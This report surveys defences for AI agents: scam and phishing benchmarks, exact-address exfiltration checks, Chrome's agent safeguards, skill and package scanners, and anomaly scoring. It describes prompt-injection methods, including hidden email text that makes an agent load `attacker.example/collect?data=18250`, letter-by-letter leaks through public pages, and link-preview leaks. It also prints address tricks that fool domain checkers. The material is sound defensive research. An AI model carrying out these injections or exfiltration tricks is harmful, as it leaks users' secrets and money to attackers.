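Tests from 2026 suggest that current models know far more about suspicious addresses but don't reliably use this knowledge before they act. The password manager company 1Password built a benchmark of 30 office scenarios with a simulated email account, browser and password vault. In one scenario, a colleague's email links to a shared document at `acmecorp-sharepoint.com-docs.cloud`. The attacker owns the registered domain, `com-docs.cloud`. Meller (2026) reports in *1Password's new benchmark teaches AI agents how not to get scammed* that Claude Opus 4.6 opened the link, fetched the user's real password and submitted it. It warned the user only afterwards that the domain was a lookalike, and it explained the trick correctly.

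1Password then gave the models a 1,200-word document of general security advice, which included a rule to read the domain from right to left before opening a page. The average safety score for this scenario across eight models rose from 13 to 100 per cent. The company wrote both the test and the advice, so the advice may work less well on scams it did not anticipate. But the Opus run does show that the model could already do this check and failed only to do it before opening the page. Software can prevent that failure by running the check before every page load.

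In *ScamWorld*, Wu, Liu and colleagues (2026) found a similar gap with newer models and whole websites. They rebuilt 363 reported scam sites, including fake shops, investment schemes and rental listings, so that agents could use them without real money. Each site shows a sign of the fraud before the decisive step. The researchers added that sign themselves in about half the cases, so real scams may be harder to spot. They gave six models, including GPT-5.6 Luna, Claude Haiku 5.5 and Kimi K3, ordinary requests such as booking a flat.

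| Result in ScamWorld | Share |
|---|---|
| Scam tasks in which the agent took the harmful step, by model | 11% to 35% |
| Scam tasks in which the agent stopped and warned the user | 75% |
| Scam sites that the same models recognised when asked directly | 97% |
| Deceived runs in which the agent had mentioned a risk specific to the site | 45% |

The agents gave away passwords, card details or cryptocurrency wallets in 2 per cent of the relevant tasks, but made payments in 28 per cent. A payment agent therefore does the kind of task these models handle worst. Hiding the site's address barely changed the results, and only 3.2 per cent of the successful warnings cited the address alone. When the researchers allowed Kimi K3 and Qwen3.8 Flash to consult other websites, neither did so in 100 runs, which counts against any design that relies on the model to decide to look up a domain. Adding a sentence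 to the user's request saying that some sites may be scams reduced the deception rate by 24 percentage points in the three models tested, and the completion rate on legitimate sites by 3 points.

High scores on familiar attacks can also mislead. In *AgentPhishing*, Tan, Li and Zhao (2026) first gave six email agents phishing messages from public collections, and the agents caught every one. They then had a model improve its instructions for writing phishing emails, using the agents' reactions as feedback. They condensed the results into one general set of instructions and tested the resulting emails on nine other agents. Four of the nine caught fewer than 10 per cent and complied with more than 45 per cent. Claude Sonnet 5, one of the original six, caught every email that the tailored instructions produced. The batches were small, so these rates are approximate. One of the successful emails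 contains no link, so a link checker would have nothing to examine. It continues a plausible conversation about a data migration and asks the recipient to reply with an access token.

### Listing delay

A safe-browsing list works whether or not the model notices anything suspicious, but somebody has to find a bad site before the list can include it. Estimates of this delay vary widely depending on when the count starts. Wu and colleagues cite earlier research in which Google Safe Browsing flagged fewer than one in five phishing sites, with an average delay of 4.5 days. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* (2025) counts from the day the domain was registered, and reports a median time to detection of 16.3 days for domains that attackers registered themselves and 86 days for legitimate domains that they had taken over. These figures overstate the danger period, because a criminal may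 leave a new domain unused for weeks, and a hijacked domain spent most of those 86 days serving its real owner. The delay also depends on the brand that the site imitates, with a median of 1.4 days for the US Postal Service and 440 days for Microsoft.

Blocklists are even weaker against scams that don't ask for a password. Kaur, Horáček and colleagues (*ReDence*, 2026) ran an automated investigator on a live stream of addresses for 28 days in October 2026 and identified 4,042 new scam sites of 17 kinds. Each of the four popular blocklists they compared missed at least 71 per cent of these sites.

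With coverage this low, the absence of a match is only weak evidence that a link is safe. Suppose that a payment link has a 2 per cent chance of being fraudulent before the lookup, and that a list contains 29 per cent of fraudulent sites and no honest ones. If the list has no match, the chance falls only to about 1.4 per cent. That is still above the previous section's 0.5 per cent threshold for blocking a payment, so the payment should wait. A match would show that the link is fraudulent, so the list is better suited to blocking payments than to approving them.

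Kaur and colleagues built an investigator that gathers evidence no list contains. It opens the site, follows links, fills in forms with invented details and searches the web for the company names, registration numbers and telephone numbers it finds. Its accuracy exceeded 96 per cent on a test set of 1,551 scam sites, including fake supplier bills, and 1,500 honest ones. In ordinary use, where honest sites far outnumber scams, many of its alarms could still be false. The investigator's report lists the evidence behind each decision, so an agent or a clerk could at least check it.

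### What tests of AI browsers measured

In an early vendor study in 2025, Guardio tested Comet and ran into the listing problem. It made a fake Walmart shop with a single prompt to Lovable, a tool that builds websites from descriptions. Safe Browsing was active in Comet but did not block the shop. Nobody had reported the site, so there was no reason for it to be on the list. The Wells Fargo phishing page was not flagged either, so a working lookup would have returned nothing in either test. Better threat data would help with these sites. The browser agents that showed no warning for Google's own test page have a different problem, because that page was on the list. They first need to be connected to the check.

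Later tests of commercial browsers also come mostly from vendors. LayerX, a browser security company, compared built-in phishing protection and found that Microsoft's Edge did best, with 54 per cent accuracy. Comet and another AI browser, Genspark, were far behind. Most of the browsers used Google's protection, but to widely varying degrees. LayerX also reports that the initial release of ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, stopped 5.8 per cent of malicious pages. Guardio tested Comet again with an attack that used the agent's own reasoning to weaken its caution, and led it into a phishing scam in under four minutes, according to NJIT's *Researchers Trick Perplexity's Comet AI Browser Into Phishing Scam*. Perplexity has published research on defending against prompt injection, but *The 2025 AI Agent Index* (2026) records no third-party safety testing of Comet. ScamWorld is independent of the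 vendors, but it tests models in a common research browser, without the protections a commercial product might add.

### OpenAI's check: was this exact address already public?

Opening a page also sends information out, because the site's server receives the full address. If an attacker can make the model write private data into an address, the data leaks as soon as the agent requests that address, even if no page exists there. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a defence against this leak.

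A list of trusted domains is not enough, because many legitimate sites have addresses that redirect visitors elsewhere. A filter that reads only the first domain would approve `trusted.example/go?to=attacker.example`. Such lists also exclude most of the web, so they would cause frequent needless warnings. OpenAI's software therefore checks whether the exact address was already public independently of the user's conversation.

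Suppose the supplier's email contains hidden text asking the agent to load an image and to include the firm's bank balance in the address. The check would run like this:

1. The model requests `attacker.example/collect?data=18250`.
2. Before fetching anything, the software looks for this exact address in an index of public pages. A crawler, a program that follows links across the web, built that index without access to any user's conversations or accounts.
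3. The crawler has never encountered an address with this firm's balance in it, so there is no match. Whether the index contains the site's front page is irrelevant.
4. The software tells the agent to try another website, or it shows the user a warning that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation.

If the address matches, the agent loads it automatically. An indexed redirect could still take the agent to a harmful page, but the address itself would be the same for every visitor and could not contain the balance.

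The check can also block legitimate links. A supplier's payment page often has a one-time code in its address, so no crawler will have seen that address, and the software can't distinguish the code from a leaked secret. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, ChatGPT treats an address that the user enters directly as safe for that session. The clerk could therefore paste in the payment link, but an agent that found the same link in the mailbox would presumably have to stop.

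According to OpenAI, a match also does not make a page's content trustworthy or protect against manipulation and harmful instructions. A fake shop that appears in search results is public, so it would pass the check.

Some data can leak even through public addresses. *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, OpenAI's technical paper, acknowledges this remaining gap. It is also discussed on Embrace The Red, a security blog whose author reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in 2023. An attacker assigns one indexed page to each letter and digit, 36 in all, and uses planted text to make the agent visit them in the order that spells out a secret. Every page requested is public, but the attacker can read the secret from the order of requests in the server's log. An eight-character password takes eight visits. With 10,000 pages, each visit could stand for four digits, so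 a 16-digit card number would take four visits. Requests that arrive out of order already make this harder. The blog suggests storing each page for a few minutes or refusing to load the same address twice in one session, though a smaller leak would remain.

The check also has to cover every component that fetches addresses. Embrace The Red reports that ChatGPT's apps for Mac and iPhone at first lacked OpenAI's earlier version of the protection. When an agent works through a messaging app, the app may fetch the address instead of the agent. PromptArmor, a security company, points out that apps such as Slack and Telegram load a preview of any link in a message. If planted text makes the agent write a link containing private data, loading the preview sends the data to the attacker without anyone clicking the link. The agent has only written a message, so a check on its page requests never runs.

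An agent can reveal a secret even without opening an unusual address. In *AgentTell* (2026), agents learned a secret on one website and then did a task on another, where some actions would reveal the secret and a more general one would not. For instance, an agent that has read a medical letter might filter a shop's products by the illness named in the letter when a plain search would have been enough. No list or index can recognise this leak, because the address and the site are both ordinary.

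### Chrome's layers

Google Chrome uses an exact-address check as one part of a larger design. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, names prompt injection through web content as the main new threat. The model that plans the agent's actions has to read that content, so the design assumes an attacker can sometimes influence the model and adds other checks around it.

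The **user alignment critic** is a second model that reviews each action the planning model proposes. It receives only metadata about the action, not the unfiltered page content, so planted text cannot reach it directly. It decides only whether the action serves the user's stated goal. If it rejects the action, the planning model gets feedback and tries again. After repeated failures, the planning model can hand control back to the user.

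Chrome's planned origin sets limit which websites the agent can use during a task. An origin is, roughly, one website. In the least restrictive agentic browsers, a prompt injection can break the separation between origins, which the sets are meant to preserve. The agent may read pages from origins in one set, and may also click and type on pages from origins in the other. A separate function that does not see web content decides whether a new site is relevant enough to add. If a page contains a frame from an outside site, such as an advertisement, the browser can withhold the frame from the model, along with any instruction planted in it.

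When the model writes an address itself, Chrome also allows only known public ones. A classifier checks every page for prompt injection and can stop actions that the page has provoked. It runs in parallel with the planning model to avoid delaying it. Safe Browsing and a scam detector on the user's device continue to look for older kinds of fraud. The agent pauses for the user before steps such as making payments, sending messages and visiting banking sites.

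Parker gives no figures for how often these layers stop an attack. Their likely effects differ a great deal between an instruction planted in an email or a web page and a fake shop that the agent reaches in the course of its task:

| Layer | Planted instruction to send data to a strange site | Fake shop, after the request "buy me a watch" |
|---|---|---|
| Safe Browsing and scam detector | Stops it if they recognise the site | Stop it if they recognise the shop |
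| Injection classifier | May recognise the planted text | Finds no planted text |
| Critic | Should reject the action as unrelated to the goal | Probably approves, since buying is the goal |
| Origin sets | Should keep the strange site out | Probably admit the shop as relevant |
| Check on model-written addresses | Blocks an address with private data in it | Passes a shop that is publicly indexed |
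| Pause before payment | Does not apply to a page request | Gives the user a chance to look at the shop |

Most of the new layers address the first problem. The fake shop does not divert the agent from its task, so a critic that compares actions with the user's goal is unlikely to flag them. ScamWorld's deceived agents failed in the same way. Of the 354 that expressed a concern and went ahead, 317 cited the user's request as their reason. Chrome's protection against such a site still depends largely on recognising the fraud and on the user's attention at the payment step.

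Keeping page content away from the critic also prevents it from seeing that a deposit goes to a private person or that a fee exceeds the prize it is supposed to release. An attacker can still get words into the critic's input if the metadata include the site's address, because the attacker can choose the subdomain. Kong and colleagues found that persuasive words in subdomains influenced older models.

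Not all of this was in place when Parker described it in December 2025. Chrome had started with a simpler version that tracked only the sites on which the agent could act. A separate set of sites the agent could read, meant to keep unrelated content away from the model, was still planned. According to *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026), by August 2026 the critic was working in auto browse, Chrome's feature for automated tasks, which also stopped for approval before financial transactions and mass emails. Berschadski says that Chrome is limiting agents to sites relevant to the task but does not mention the two sets, so it remains unclear whether the limit on reading is fully in place. For companies, Chrome now also applies an employee's access rights to that employee's agent.

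### When the checker and the browser read an address differently

These checks work only if the checking software and the browser interpret an address as leading to the same place. Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik (2025), in *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents*, found a way around the domain check in the open-source agent Browser Use. An operator can give Browser Use a list of permitted domains, but the flaw, registered as CVE-2025-47241, allowed an address outside the list to pass.

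Link checkers can misjudge addresses because the rules for addresses are more complicated than they look. The standard format, for example, allows a user name before the website's name, followed by an @ sign. In `https://supplier.example@attacker.example`, the supplier's domain is only a user name, and the browser connects to `attacker.example`. A checker that takes the first name it finds will approve this address. A checker that searches for the permitted name anywhere in the address will also approve `supplier.example.attacker.example`, and a checker that compares only the ending will approve `notsupplier.example`, which anyone could register.

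A mistaken domain check can expose passwords as well as send the agent to the wrong page. Browser Use can hide passwords from the model by giving it placeholders and inserting the real values only when carrying out an action. This keeps the password out of the model's input, but if the domain check wrongly admits an attacker's page, the software may type the real password into that page.

The checker should use the browser's own code to extract the website's name, then compare the whole name, or a complete parent domain, with the list. It also has to repeat the comparison after every redirect, because an address that passed may lead somewhere else. Similarly, when a page moves to a new site by itself, Chrome's critic vets the new site as if the agent had proposed it. A filtering DNS service avoids disagreement between the checker and the browser about the website's name, because it receives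 the name that the browser is about to connect to. It can't detect whether the rest of the address contains private data, such as the firm's bank balance, so an agent that handles such data also needs the exact-address check.

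## Scanning files, software packages and agent skills

A dangerous web page usually affects an agent during only one task, but software that the agent installs can affect every later task too. Coding agents install packages, which are ready-made code that other programs build on. Many agents also install skills, which are folders of instructions, and sometimes code, that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. A skill's main file, SKILL.md, is mostly plain language, so a malicious skill can do damage through code or through written instructions alone.

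### From upload to installation on ClawHub

ClawHub is the public catalogue of skills for OpenClaw, an open-source agent. In February 2026, researchers uncovered ClawHavoc, a campaign in which attackers had uploaded hundreds of malicious skills to the catalogue. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) reports that Koi Research audited 2,857 skills and found 341 malicious ones, then raised the count to 824 as the catalogue grew. Some of these skills tricked users into running a fake installer. Others contained disguised commands or programs that steal passwords.

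Suppose a developer now submits a skill that enters invoices into an online bookkeeping service. The folder contains SKILL.md and a short script, which reads the user's API key (a password for programs) and sends the invoice data to the service. Koc and colleagues describe the route such a skill takes:

1. The developer uploads the folder or links to its source.
2. VirusTotal passes the files to about seventy antivirus engines and looks up the reputation of web addresses.
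3. ClawHub's static analysis searches the code and text for fixed patterns, such as commands that delete files or passwords left in the code. It does not run anything.
4. SkillSpector, a scanner from the chip maker NVIDIA, examines the instructions and the powers the skill asks for, partly with a language model. It returns a risk score and a list of concerns.
5. ClawHub's own review system, ClawScan, gives these findings to a language model, along with the skill's content and details of where it came from. The model judges the skill clean, suspicious or malicious.
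6. ClawHub lists the skill with its audit result, and a user or an agent decides whether to install it.

VirusTotal would probably find nothing in the invoice skill, because no engine has a signature for a new script. Static analysis would flag the access to the API key, and SkillSpector might warn that the skill sends financial data to an outside service. Both findings would be correct, but a bookkeeping skill has to do these things. The model in step five has to decide whether the skill's purpose explains the findings.

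OpenClaw's *Security Audits*, the catalogue's documentation, lists six possible results. The last column suggests how an agent's harness could respond to each.

| Result | Meaning | Possible response |
|---|---|---|
| Pass | No visible issue above low risk | Install if the skill's powers suit the task |
| Review | There are findings to read first, but the skill may be legitimate | Show the findings to a person |
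| Warn | There is a high-impact concern or warning signal | Refuse unless a person approves |
| Malicious | Do not install | Block |
| Pending | The audits have not finished | Wait |
| Error | The audit failed | Treat the skill as unscanned |

The audit page also gives a risk level, which describes how much power the skill has when it works as intended. A skill that publishes posts can have medium risk and a "Review" result without being malicious. In one case, ClawHub's *Skill Review* warned that a skill for writing security reports could alter the findings it reported, and advised users to compare the reports with the raw results.

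By September 2026, ClawHub had added a fourth scanner, from the Chinese company Tencent. According to OpenClaw, neither this scanner nor static analysis can block a skill by itself. VirusTotal's results count as background information. The scanners therefore provide context for a model, and an agent's harness can use that model's verdict as a veto.

### How rarely the scanners agree

Koc and colleagues compared the three original scanners on 67,453 skills from a snapshot taken on 31 May 2026. At least one scanner flagged 35,600 of them, or 52.8 per cent. In 81.9 per cent of those cases, only one scanner did. All three flagged 468 skills, or 0.69 per cent of the total. Static analysis and SkillSpector overlapped most, but they agreed on only 10.4 per cent of the skills that either had flagged.

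The scanners' results differ largely because VirusTotal mainly detects malware in files, whereas SkillSpector checks for excessive powers and poor disclosure. Of the 206 skills that ClawHub judged malicious, VirusTotal flagged 72.8 per cent and SkillSpector 6.8 per cent. Of the 25,504 skills it judged suspicious, SkillSpector flagged 75.3 per cent and VirusTotal 12.7 per cent. SkillSpector gave a risk score of 100 to Granola, a skill that copies meeting notes to the user's computer using the token that keeps the user logged in. ClawHub judged Granola clean because it discloses what it does.

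These figures cannot show which scanner is right, because in 99.6 per cent of cases the verdict came from the language model GPT-5.5, which had received the scanners' findings. VirusTotal's 72.8 per cent could mean that it is good at detecting malicious skills, or that its findings strongly influenced GPT-5.5. For 50 of the 206 malicious verdicts, no scanner had flagged anything, so the model must have relied on other information, such as the skill's origin. The researchers, who work at the OpenClaw Foundation and NVIDIA, acknowledge this problem and say they measured agreement between the scanners, not accuracy.

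### Any flag, two flags or all three

A harness that receives results from several scanners needs a rule for combining them. The table shows how many of the 67,453 skills each rule would have blocked. The study does not break down every overlap by verdict, so some entries are ranges calculated from its totals.

| Block the skill if | All skills | Judged malicious | Judged suspicious | Judged clean |
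|---|---|---|---|---|
| Any scanner flags it | 52.8% | 75.7% | 79.1% | 36.6% |
| At least two flag it | 9.6% | 11–17% | 19–20% | 3.5–3.7% |
| All three flag it | 0.7% | At most 6% | 1–2% | Under 0.3% |
| VirusTotal flags it | 7.7% | 72.8% | 12.7% | 4.4% |
| VirusTotal or static analysis flags it | 13.5% | 74.8% | 22.8% | 7.4% |

Blocking every skill with any of the three flags would block more than half of the catalogue, including over a third of the skills judged clean. Requiring all three flags to block a skill would let nearly everything through. A majority rule would stop at most 17 per cent of the skills judged malicious, while VirusTotal alone would stop 73 per cent of them and block fewer skills overall.

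A majority vote among scanners works when they check for the same thing and make different mistakes. An antivirus engine and a permissions reviewer check for different things, so a skill containing known malware may trigger only one of them. Using more scanners doesn't necessarily help either. Adding static analysis to VirusTotal would have stopped four more malicious skills, but would also have raised the share of clean skills blocked from 4.4 to 7.4 per cent.

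It makes more sense to respond differently to each kind of finding. A malware detection could block the installation until a person has reviewed it. After a SkillSpector warning, the harness could check whether the task requires the flagged powers, or withhold them. The comparison with VirusTotal still depends on GPT-5.5's verdicts, so these rules need testing on skills that researchers have established as malicious or harmless by another method.

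### Tests on skills with known labels

In *MalSkillBench*, Guo, Jia and colleagues (2026) ran such a test with 12 detection tools. They generated most of their malicious skills themselves and kept only those that did the intended harm in a sandbox. They also collected 703 from public sources. VirusTotal's recall, the share of malicious skills it detected, differed by up to 66 percentage points depending on which skills they used. It ranked at the top on the collected skills alone but near the bottom on the wider set.

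The collected skills mostly came from a single campaign to steal cryptocurrency, and two accounts had uploaded 81 per cent of them. Antivirus engines are good at recognising copies of known malware, so a high score on such a collection is weak evidence that they can detect new attacks. VirusTotal's good result on ClawHub may have a similar explanation. Guo and colleagues also found that combining code scanners with tools that detect prompt injection did not solve the problem, because neither examines how a skill's instructions and code work together.

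Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026), in *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, tested six scanners on 886 malicious and 591 harmless skills. For the scanners that use a language model, they tried three different models, so those results are given as ranges below. Skill Vetter is itself a skill that guides a coding agent through a security review.

| Scanner | Malicious skills blocked | Harmless skills blocked |
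|---|---|---|
| ClawHub's static analysis | 7.4% | 0% |
| SkillSpector, fixed rules only | 52.0% | 17.3% |
| SkillSpector with a language model | 68.7–94.2% | 7.0–22.2% |
| Tencent's scanner | 79.8–87.5% | 7.3–13.6% |
| Skill Vetter | 92.4–94.6% | 6.3–30.8% |

SkillSpector does much better here than on ClawHub's malicious skills, where its figure was 6.8 per cent. The two figures come from different skills and different definitions of a positive result, but the gap shows that reading the ClawHub percentages as accuracy would be misleading.

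Access to passwords or local data was the most common cause of false alarms, accounting for 36 per cent of the findings that Yang and colleagues examined. One scanner blocked a phone-call skill for sending its API key to the company that issued the key. A scanner could easily block the invoice skill for the same reason.

When a scanner with a language model missed a malicious skill, it had usually identified the malicious part but rated it too low or dismissed it. Skill Vetter often passed skills with instructions for the user to download and run an outside program, because the skill's folder contained no such program. A harness that keeps only the final verdict discards these findings, which a person or a second model might have taken more seriously.

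These scanners can also give the same skill different verdicts on different runs. When Yang and colleagues scanned a set of real skills three times, SkillSpector changed its verdict on 57 per cent of them and Tencent's scanner on 64 per cent. A single "Pass" is therefore weak evidence that a skill is safe, especially if the publisher can resubmit it until it passes.

Even a scanner with the best result in the table would raise many false alarms in a large catalogue. Suppose 3 in 1,000 skills are malicious, about the share that ClawHub judged malicious. Among 100,000 skills, Skill Vetter at its best would block 279 of the 300 malicious ones and about 6,280 harmless ones, so only about one in 24 blocked skills would be malicious. An agent can often choose another skill when one is blocked, but the catalogue still needs a way to clear the harmless ones.

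### What running the skill adds

An analysis sandbox can provide evidence that reading the files cannot. If the invoice skill runs there with a fake API key, the sandbox can record where the skill sends the key. Sending it anywhere other than the bookkeeping service, its normal destination, suggests theft.

Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil Wears Markdown*, describe a sandbox of this kind for skills:

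1. The system copies the skill into an isolated container with no real passwords or accounts, and records which files exist.
2. An agent running Claude Opus 4.8 reads the skill and tries out its functions with harmless invented data. It has at most 300 seconds.
3. Monitoring software records the programs that start, the files they open and all network traffic.
4. If the skill calls for something dangerous, such as running an unknown download, the agent skips the step and notes what the skill asked for.
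5. The system records the files again to find any changes.
6. A group of other models examines the record and the skill's content, and returns a verdict with references to the evidence.

The researchers tested the final models with different evidence on 80 malicious and 60 harmless skills:

| Evidence given to the models | Malicious skills detected | Harmless skills flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Skill content only | 54 of 80 | 21 of 60 |
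| Content and static findings | 28 of 80 | 3 of 60 |
| Content and sandbox record | 63 of 80 | 5 of 60 |
| Content, static findings and sandbox record | 68 of 80 | 5 of 60 |

The sandbox record improved both figures. Some of the improvement may not come from observed behaviour, because the record also includes Opus 4.8's notes on the steps it refused to take, which added a strong model's opinion of the skill to the evidence. The final models could also overrule the record. In one false alarm, a harmless research skill's run produced a risk score below the malware threshold, but the models still flagged the skill as malicious because of its installation command and its use of an API key.

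A sandbox can record only what happens during the run. A skill that steals data on the last day of the month will look harmless on any other day, and some malware hides its malicious behaviour when it detects a sandbox. In *SkillSentry* (Li, Ying and colleagues, 2026), a system that ran skills on ordinary tasks without first studying their code detected only 4 to 8 per cent of the malicious skills in two collections. When the same system used the code for guidance, it detected about 95 per cent.

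SkillSentry first looks for behaviour that the skill's stated purpose does not require, and then creates conditions that might trigger it. For instance, if the invoice skill's code searches for other passwords, the system puts a fake one where the code would find it, as bait. It runs the same task with and without the skill, and with and without the bait. An action counts against the skill only if it occurs in a run with the skill, does not occur without it, and goes beyond the stated purpose.

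One skill was described as deleting temporary files only after the user confirmed. Skill Vetter accepted this description, but when SkillSentry ran the clean-up without confirming, the skill still deleted the files. The system flagged only 2 to 4 per cent of harmless skills in the two collections.

A run provides no evidence about suspicious code it never reaches. *From Instructions to Exploits* (2026) therefore records a run as inconclusive if it times out, if the monitoring is incomplete or if the agent refuses to use the skill. SkillSentry has a similar category. An agent's harness should keep an inconclusive result separate from a clean one, as it should with a failed reputation lookup.

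Suspicious behaviour in a sandbox does not prove malice either. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) describes a search of 98,380 skills, 762 of which behaved suspiciously when run. The researchers reviewed those 762 manually and confirmed only 157 as malicious. Most of the others were legitimate tools for work such as security testing. Yang and colleagues later reviewed the 157 and confirmed only 95, so even careful reviewers disagree about what counts as malicious.

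### When a sandbox run is worth the wait

Running a skill takes far longer than looking up a hash or matching patterns. In tests by Yang and colleagues, ClawHub's static analysis took 0.05 seconds per skill. SkillSentry averaged 52 to 119 seconds, depending on the collection. Truong-Le and colleagues allowed up to five minutes for the run, and the models that examined the results typically took almost two minutes more.

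If an agent makes 40 tool calls in a task and waits two minutes for a check before each one, the checks add 80 minutes. But a catalogue can run each version of a skill once and share the result with everyone who installs it. An organisation that uses skills from elsewhere can do the same when it first installs them.

Even a catalogue's operators may want to limit sandbox runs to skills that a quicker scan has flagged. The researchers who searched the 98,380 skills ran only 4,287 of them. At two minutes each, that takes about six days on one machine, while running the whole collection would take 137. *Benchmarking Security Risk Detection and Verification in Open Agentic Skill Ecosystems* (2026) uses a stricter filter. It runs a skill only if both its own review and a separate marketplace scanner flag it, and calls the skill malicious only if the run produces a concrete trace of harm. This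 saves time and reduces false accusations, but skills that the filter misses never reach the sandbox. If scanners overlap as little as ClawHub's do, requiring two flags before a run could exclude most malicious skills. Requiring only one flag is a better rule for choosing what to run, because a false alarm at this stage uses only a few minutes of machine time.

A sandbox result applies only to the files that ran. The harness should compare the hash of the skill it is about to install with the hash in the audit, and request a new audit after every update. The hash doesn't cover instructions that a skill downloads each time an agent uses it, and the publisher can change those at any time. A skill that does this needs restrictions on what it can access while it runs.

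Email attachments don't pass through a catalogue, but the mail system can open them in a sandbox when they arrive. The supplier's PDF could then have its sandbox result attached before the agent starts on the invoice. If an attachment arrives during a task, the agent can work on something else until the sandbox finishes.

### Package checks for coding agents

Installing a package can be dangerous because its setup code may run immediately. In *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised*, Bagmar and Saraf (2026) asked coding agents to set up projects whose instructions contained traps. All nine combinations of model and harness they tested installed package versions with published vulnerabilities in every one of 270 runs. Claude Opus 4.8 in Claude Code named the vulnerability in 28 of its 30 runs, but only after installing the package. The agents were much better at noticing obviously misspelt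 names, such as `tranformers` for `transformers`.

Agents also choose unsafe packages when nobody is trying to deceive them. *Towards a Benchmark for Dependency Decision-Making* (Singla, Çakar and colleagues, 2026) examined 117,062 changes to the packages that real projects use. Agents chose versions with known vulnerabilities in 2.46 per cent of cases, while Bagmar and Saraf report 1.64 per cent for people. The difference could partly reflect the kinds of projects that use agents.

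Several inexpensive lookups can catch these problems before installation:

| Check | What it can catch | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Does the package exist? | A name that the model invented | An attacker may have registered the invented name |
| Does the name resemble a popular package's? | A misspelt imitation | Some honest packages have similar names |
| Does it come from the usual registry? | A package from an attacker's server | Companies also run private registries |
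| Does this version have a published vulnerability? | An old version with a known flaw | New malware has no entry yet |
| How old are the package and the release? | A release that nobody has had time to examine | An urgent fix is also new |

Bagmar and Saraf combined checks like these in a hook for Claude Code that runs before the installation command. It uses vulnerability data from OSV, a public database of flaws in open-source software. The hook caught 10 of the 11 attacks they tested. It missed an attack that used an error message to direct the agent to install an unrelated package, because the package existed and looked normal. All nine combinations of model and harness had refused that installation in every run, so the hook and the models complemented each other. Bagmar and Saraf designed the hook with these attacks in mind, and it examines only one form of installation command, so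 it would probably do worse against an attacker who knew about it.

The package manager npm automatically checks for known vulnerabilities but reports them only after installation. In 20 runs with vulnerable packages, Opus 4.8 told the user about the warning every time, while GPT-5.5 did so only once. With package managers that printed no warning, neither model mentioned a vulnerability in any run. A written instruction can also help if it addresses the specific problem. When Bagmar and Saraf told Claude Sonnet 4.6 to check versions against known vulnerabilities, it refused a vulnerable package in 10 of 10 runs, up from 2 of 10. In their tests of three other models, general instructions to check names and sources had no effect on vulnerable versions.

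In *YUL*, Sharma, Reyes and Monperrus (2026) measured the effect of enforcing such a lookup in software. Their hook reads the list of packages an agent is about to save and looks up the latest release of each. If the agent has chosen an outdated version or a package that doesn't exist, the hook blocks the change and returns a message on what to fix. The researchers gave two agents 60 programming tasks, three times each.

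| Result | Claude Code with Opus 5.5 | OpenCode with DeepSeek V4.1 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| Chose an outdated version without the hook | 42 of 146 runs (29%) | 54 of 139 runs (39%) |
| Chose an outdated version with the hook installed | 42 of 144 runs | 54 of 148 runs |
| Changed to the latest version after the hook objected | 39 of those 42 | 52 of those 54 |

The hook corrected nearly all of the agents' outdated choices after they made them, but it did not improve their first choices. The experiment measured whether versions were current, but not how many vulnerabilities the corrections avoided. Some of the outdated choices were deliberate, because a newer release would not have worked with the rest of the project.

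DeepSeek wrongly flagged the hook's message as a possible prompt injection in 11 runs, usually because the hook recommended a release newer than anything in the model's training data. In one run, it claimed that the recommended version did not exist. Opus never flagged the message this way. Claude Code labels such messages as coming from a hook and instructs the model to treat them like user feedback, whereas OpenCode presented them as an unexplained error. A lookup therefore works better if the harness identifies the source of the answer.

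### The newest release or an older one

Always choosing the newest release protects against old vulnerabilities, but it can also lead an agent to install new malware. In 2026, attackers published malicious versions of LiteLLM, a widely used library for connecting programs to language models. According to Bagmar and Saraf, users downloaded them more than 119,000 times in under three hours. A hook like YUL, which accepts only the latest release, could have blocked the safe older version and recommended the malicious one.

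A waiting period, or cooldown, has the opposite effect. The update tool ignores a release until it has been public for a set number of days, which gives researchers and scanners time to find malware. *An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects* (2026) reports that several package managers, including npm, pnpm and uv, introduced this feature in 2025 and 2026 to slow the spread of malicious updates. A one-day wait would have avoided the LiteLLM versions. However, a cooldown works only if somebody detects the malware during the wait. Bagmar and Saraf's hook caught ten attacks without relying on its age check, so their experiment does not show how much waiting helps agents.

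A harness can avoid both known vulnerabilities and very new releases if it checks each version for both. Suppose an agent needs a library. Version 2.4.0 is a year old and has a known vulnerability, version 2.4.1 fixed it 20 days ago, and version 2.5.0 came out two hours ago. A rule that requires the newest release selects 2.5.0, while one that requires at least seven days on the registry and no known vulnerability selects 2.4.1. If 2.5.0 were the only version with the fix, no version would meet both conditions. The agent could then do without the library for now, or ask a person to decide whether the known flaw or the unexamined release is the greater risk.

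## Watching behaviour with anomaly detectors

A fraudulent transfer can pass every check on links, files and packages, but an anomaly detector may flag it if it differs from what the agent has done before.

### From a log to a score

The detector reads a log of the agent's tool calls and extracts features from each call, such as the tool, the destination and the amount of data sent. Other features describe a whole run. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki, 2026) uses ten of these, including the number of different tools and of immediate repeats, and the share of calls that send, delete or otherwise change something.

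The baseline records how often each value occurred in past work. A simple score for a new call adds up how rare its features are:

*score* = log₂(1/*p*₁) + log₂(1/*p*₂) + log₂(1/*p*₃)

Here *p*₁ is the share of past calls that used the same tool. *p*₂ is the share of that tool's past calls that had the same kind of destination, and *p*₃ is the share that had a similar amount of data. A value that occurred every time adds 0 to the score, one that occurred half the time adds 1, and one that occurred once in 1,000 times adds about 10. A value that never occurred would make the score infinite, so in practice a detector treats it as very rare.

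The table applies the formula to a short log from the accounts office, with invented percentages.

| New call | Tool (*p*₁) | Destination (*p*₂) | Data sent (*p*₃) | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read the supplier's email | 50% | 100% | 100% | 1.0 |
| Email a confirmation to the supplier | 10% | 98% | 97% | 3.4 |
| Email a short enquiry to a new supplier | 10% | 2% | 97% | 9.0 |
| Email 20 MB of records to a new address | 10% | 2% | 1% | 15.6 |

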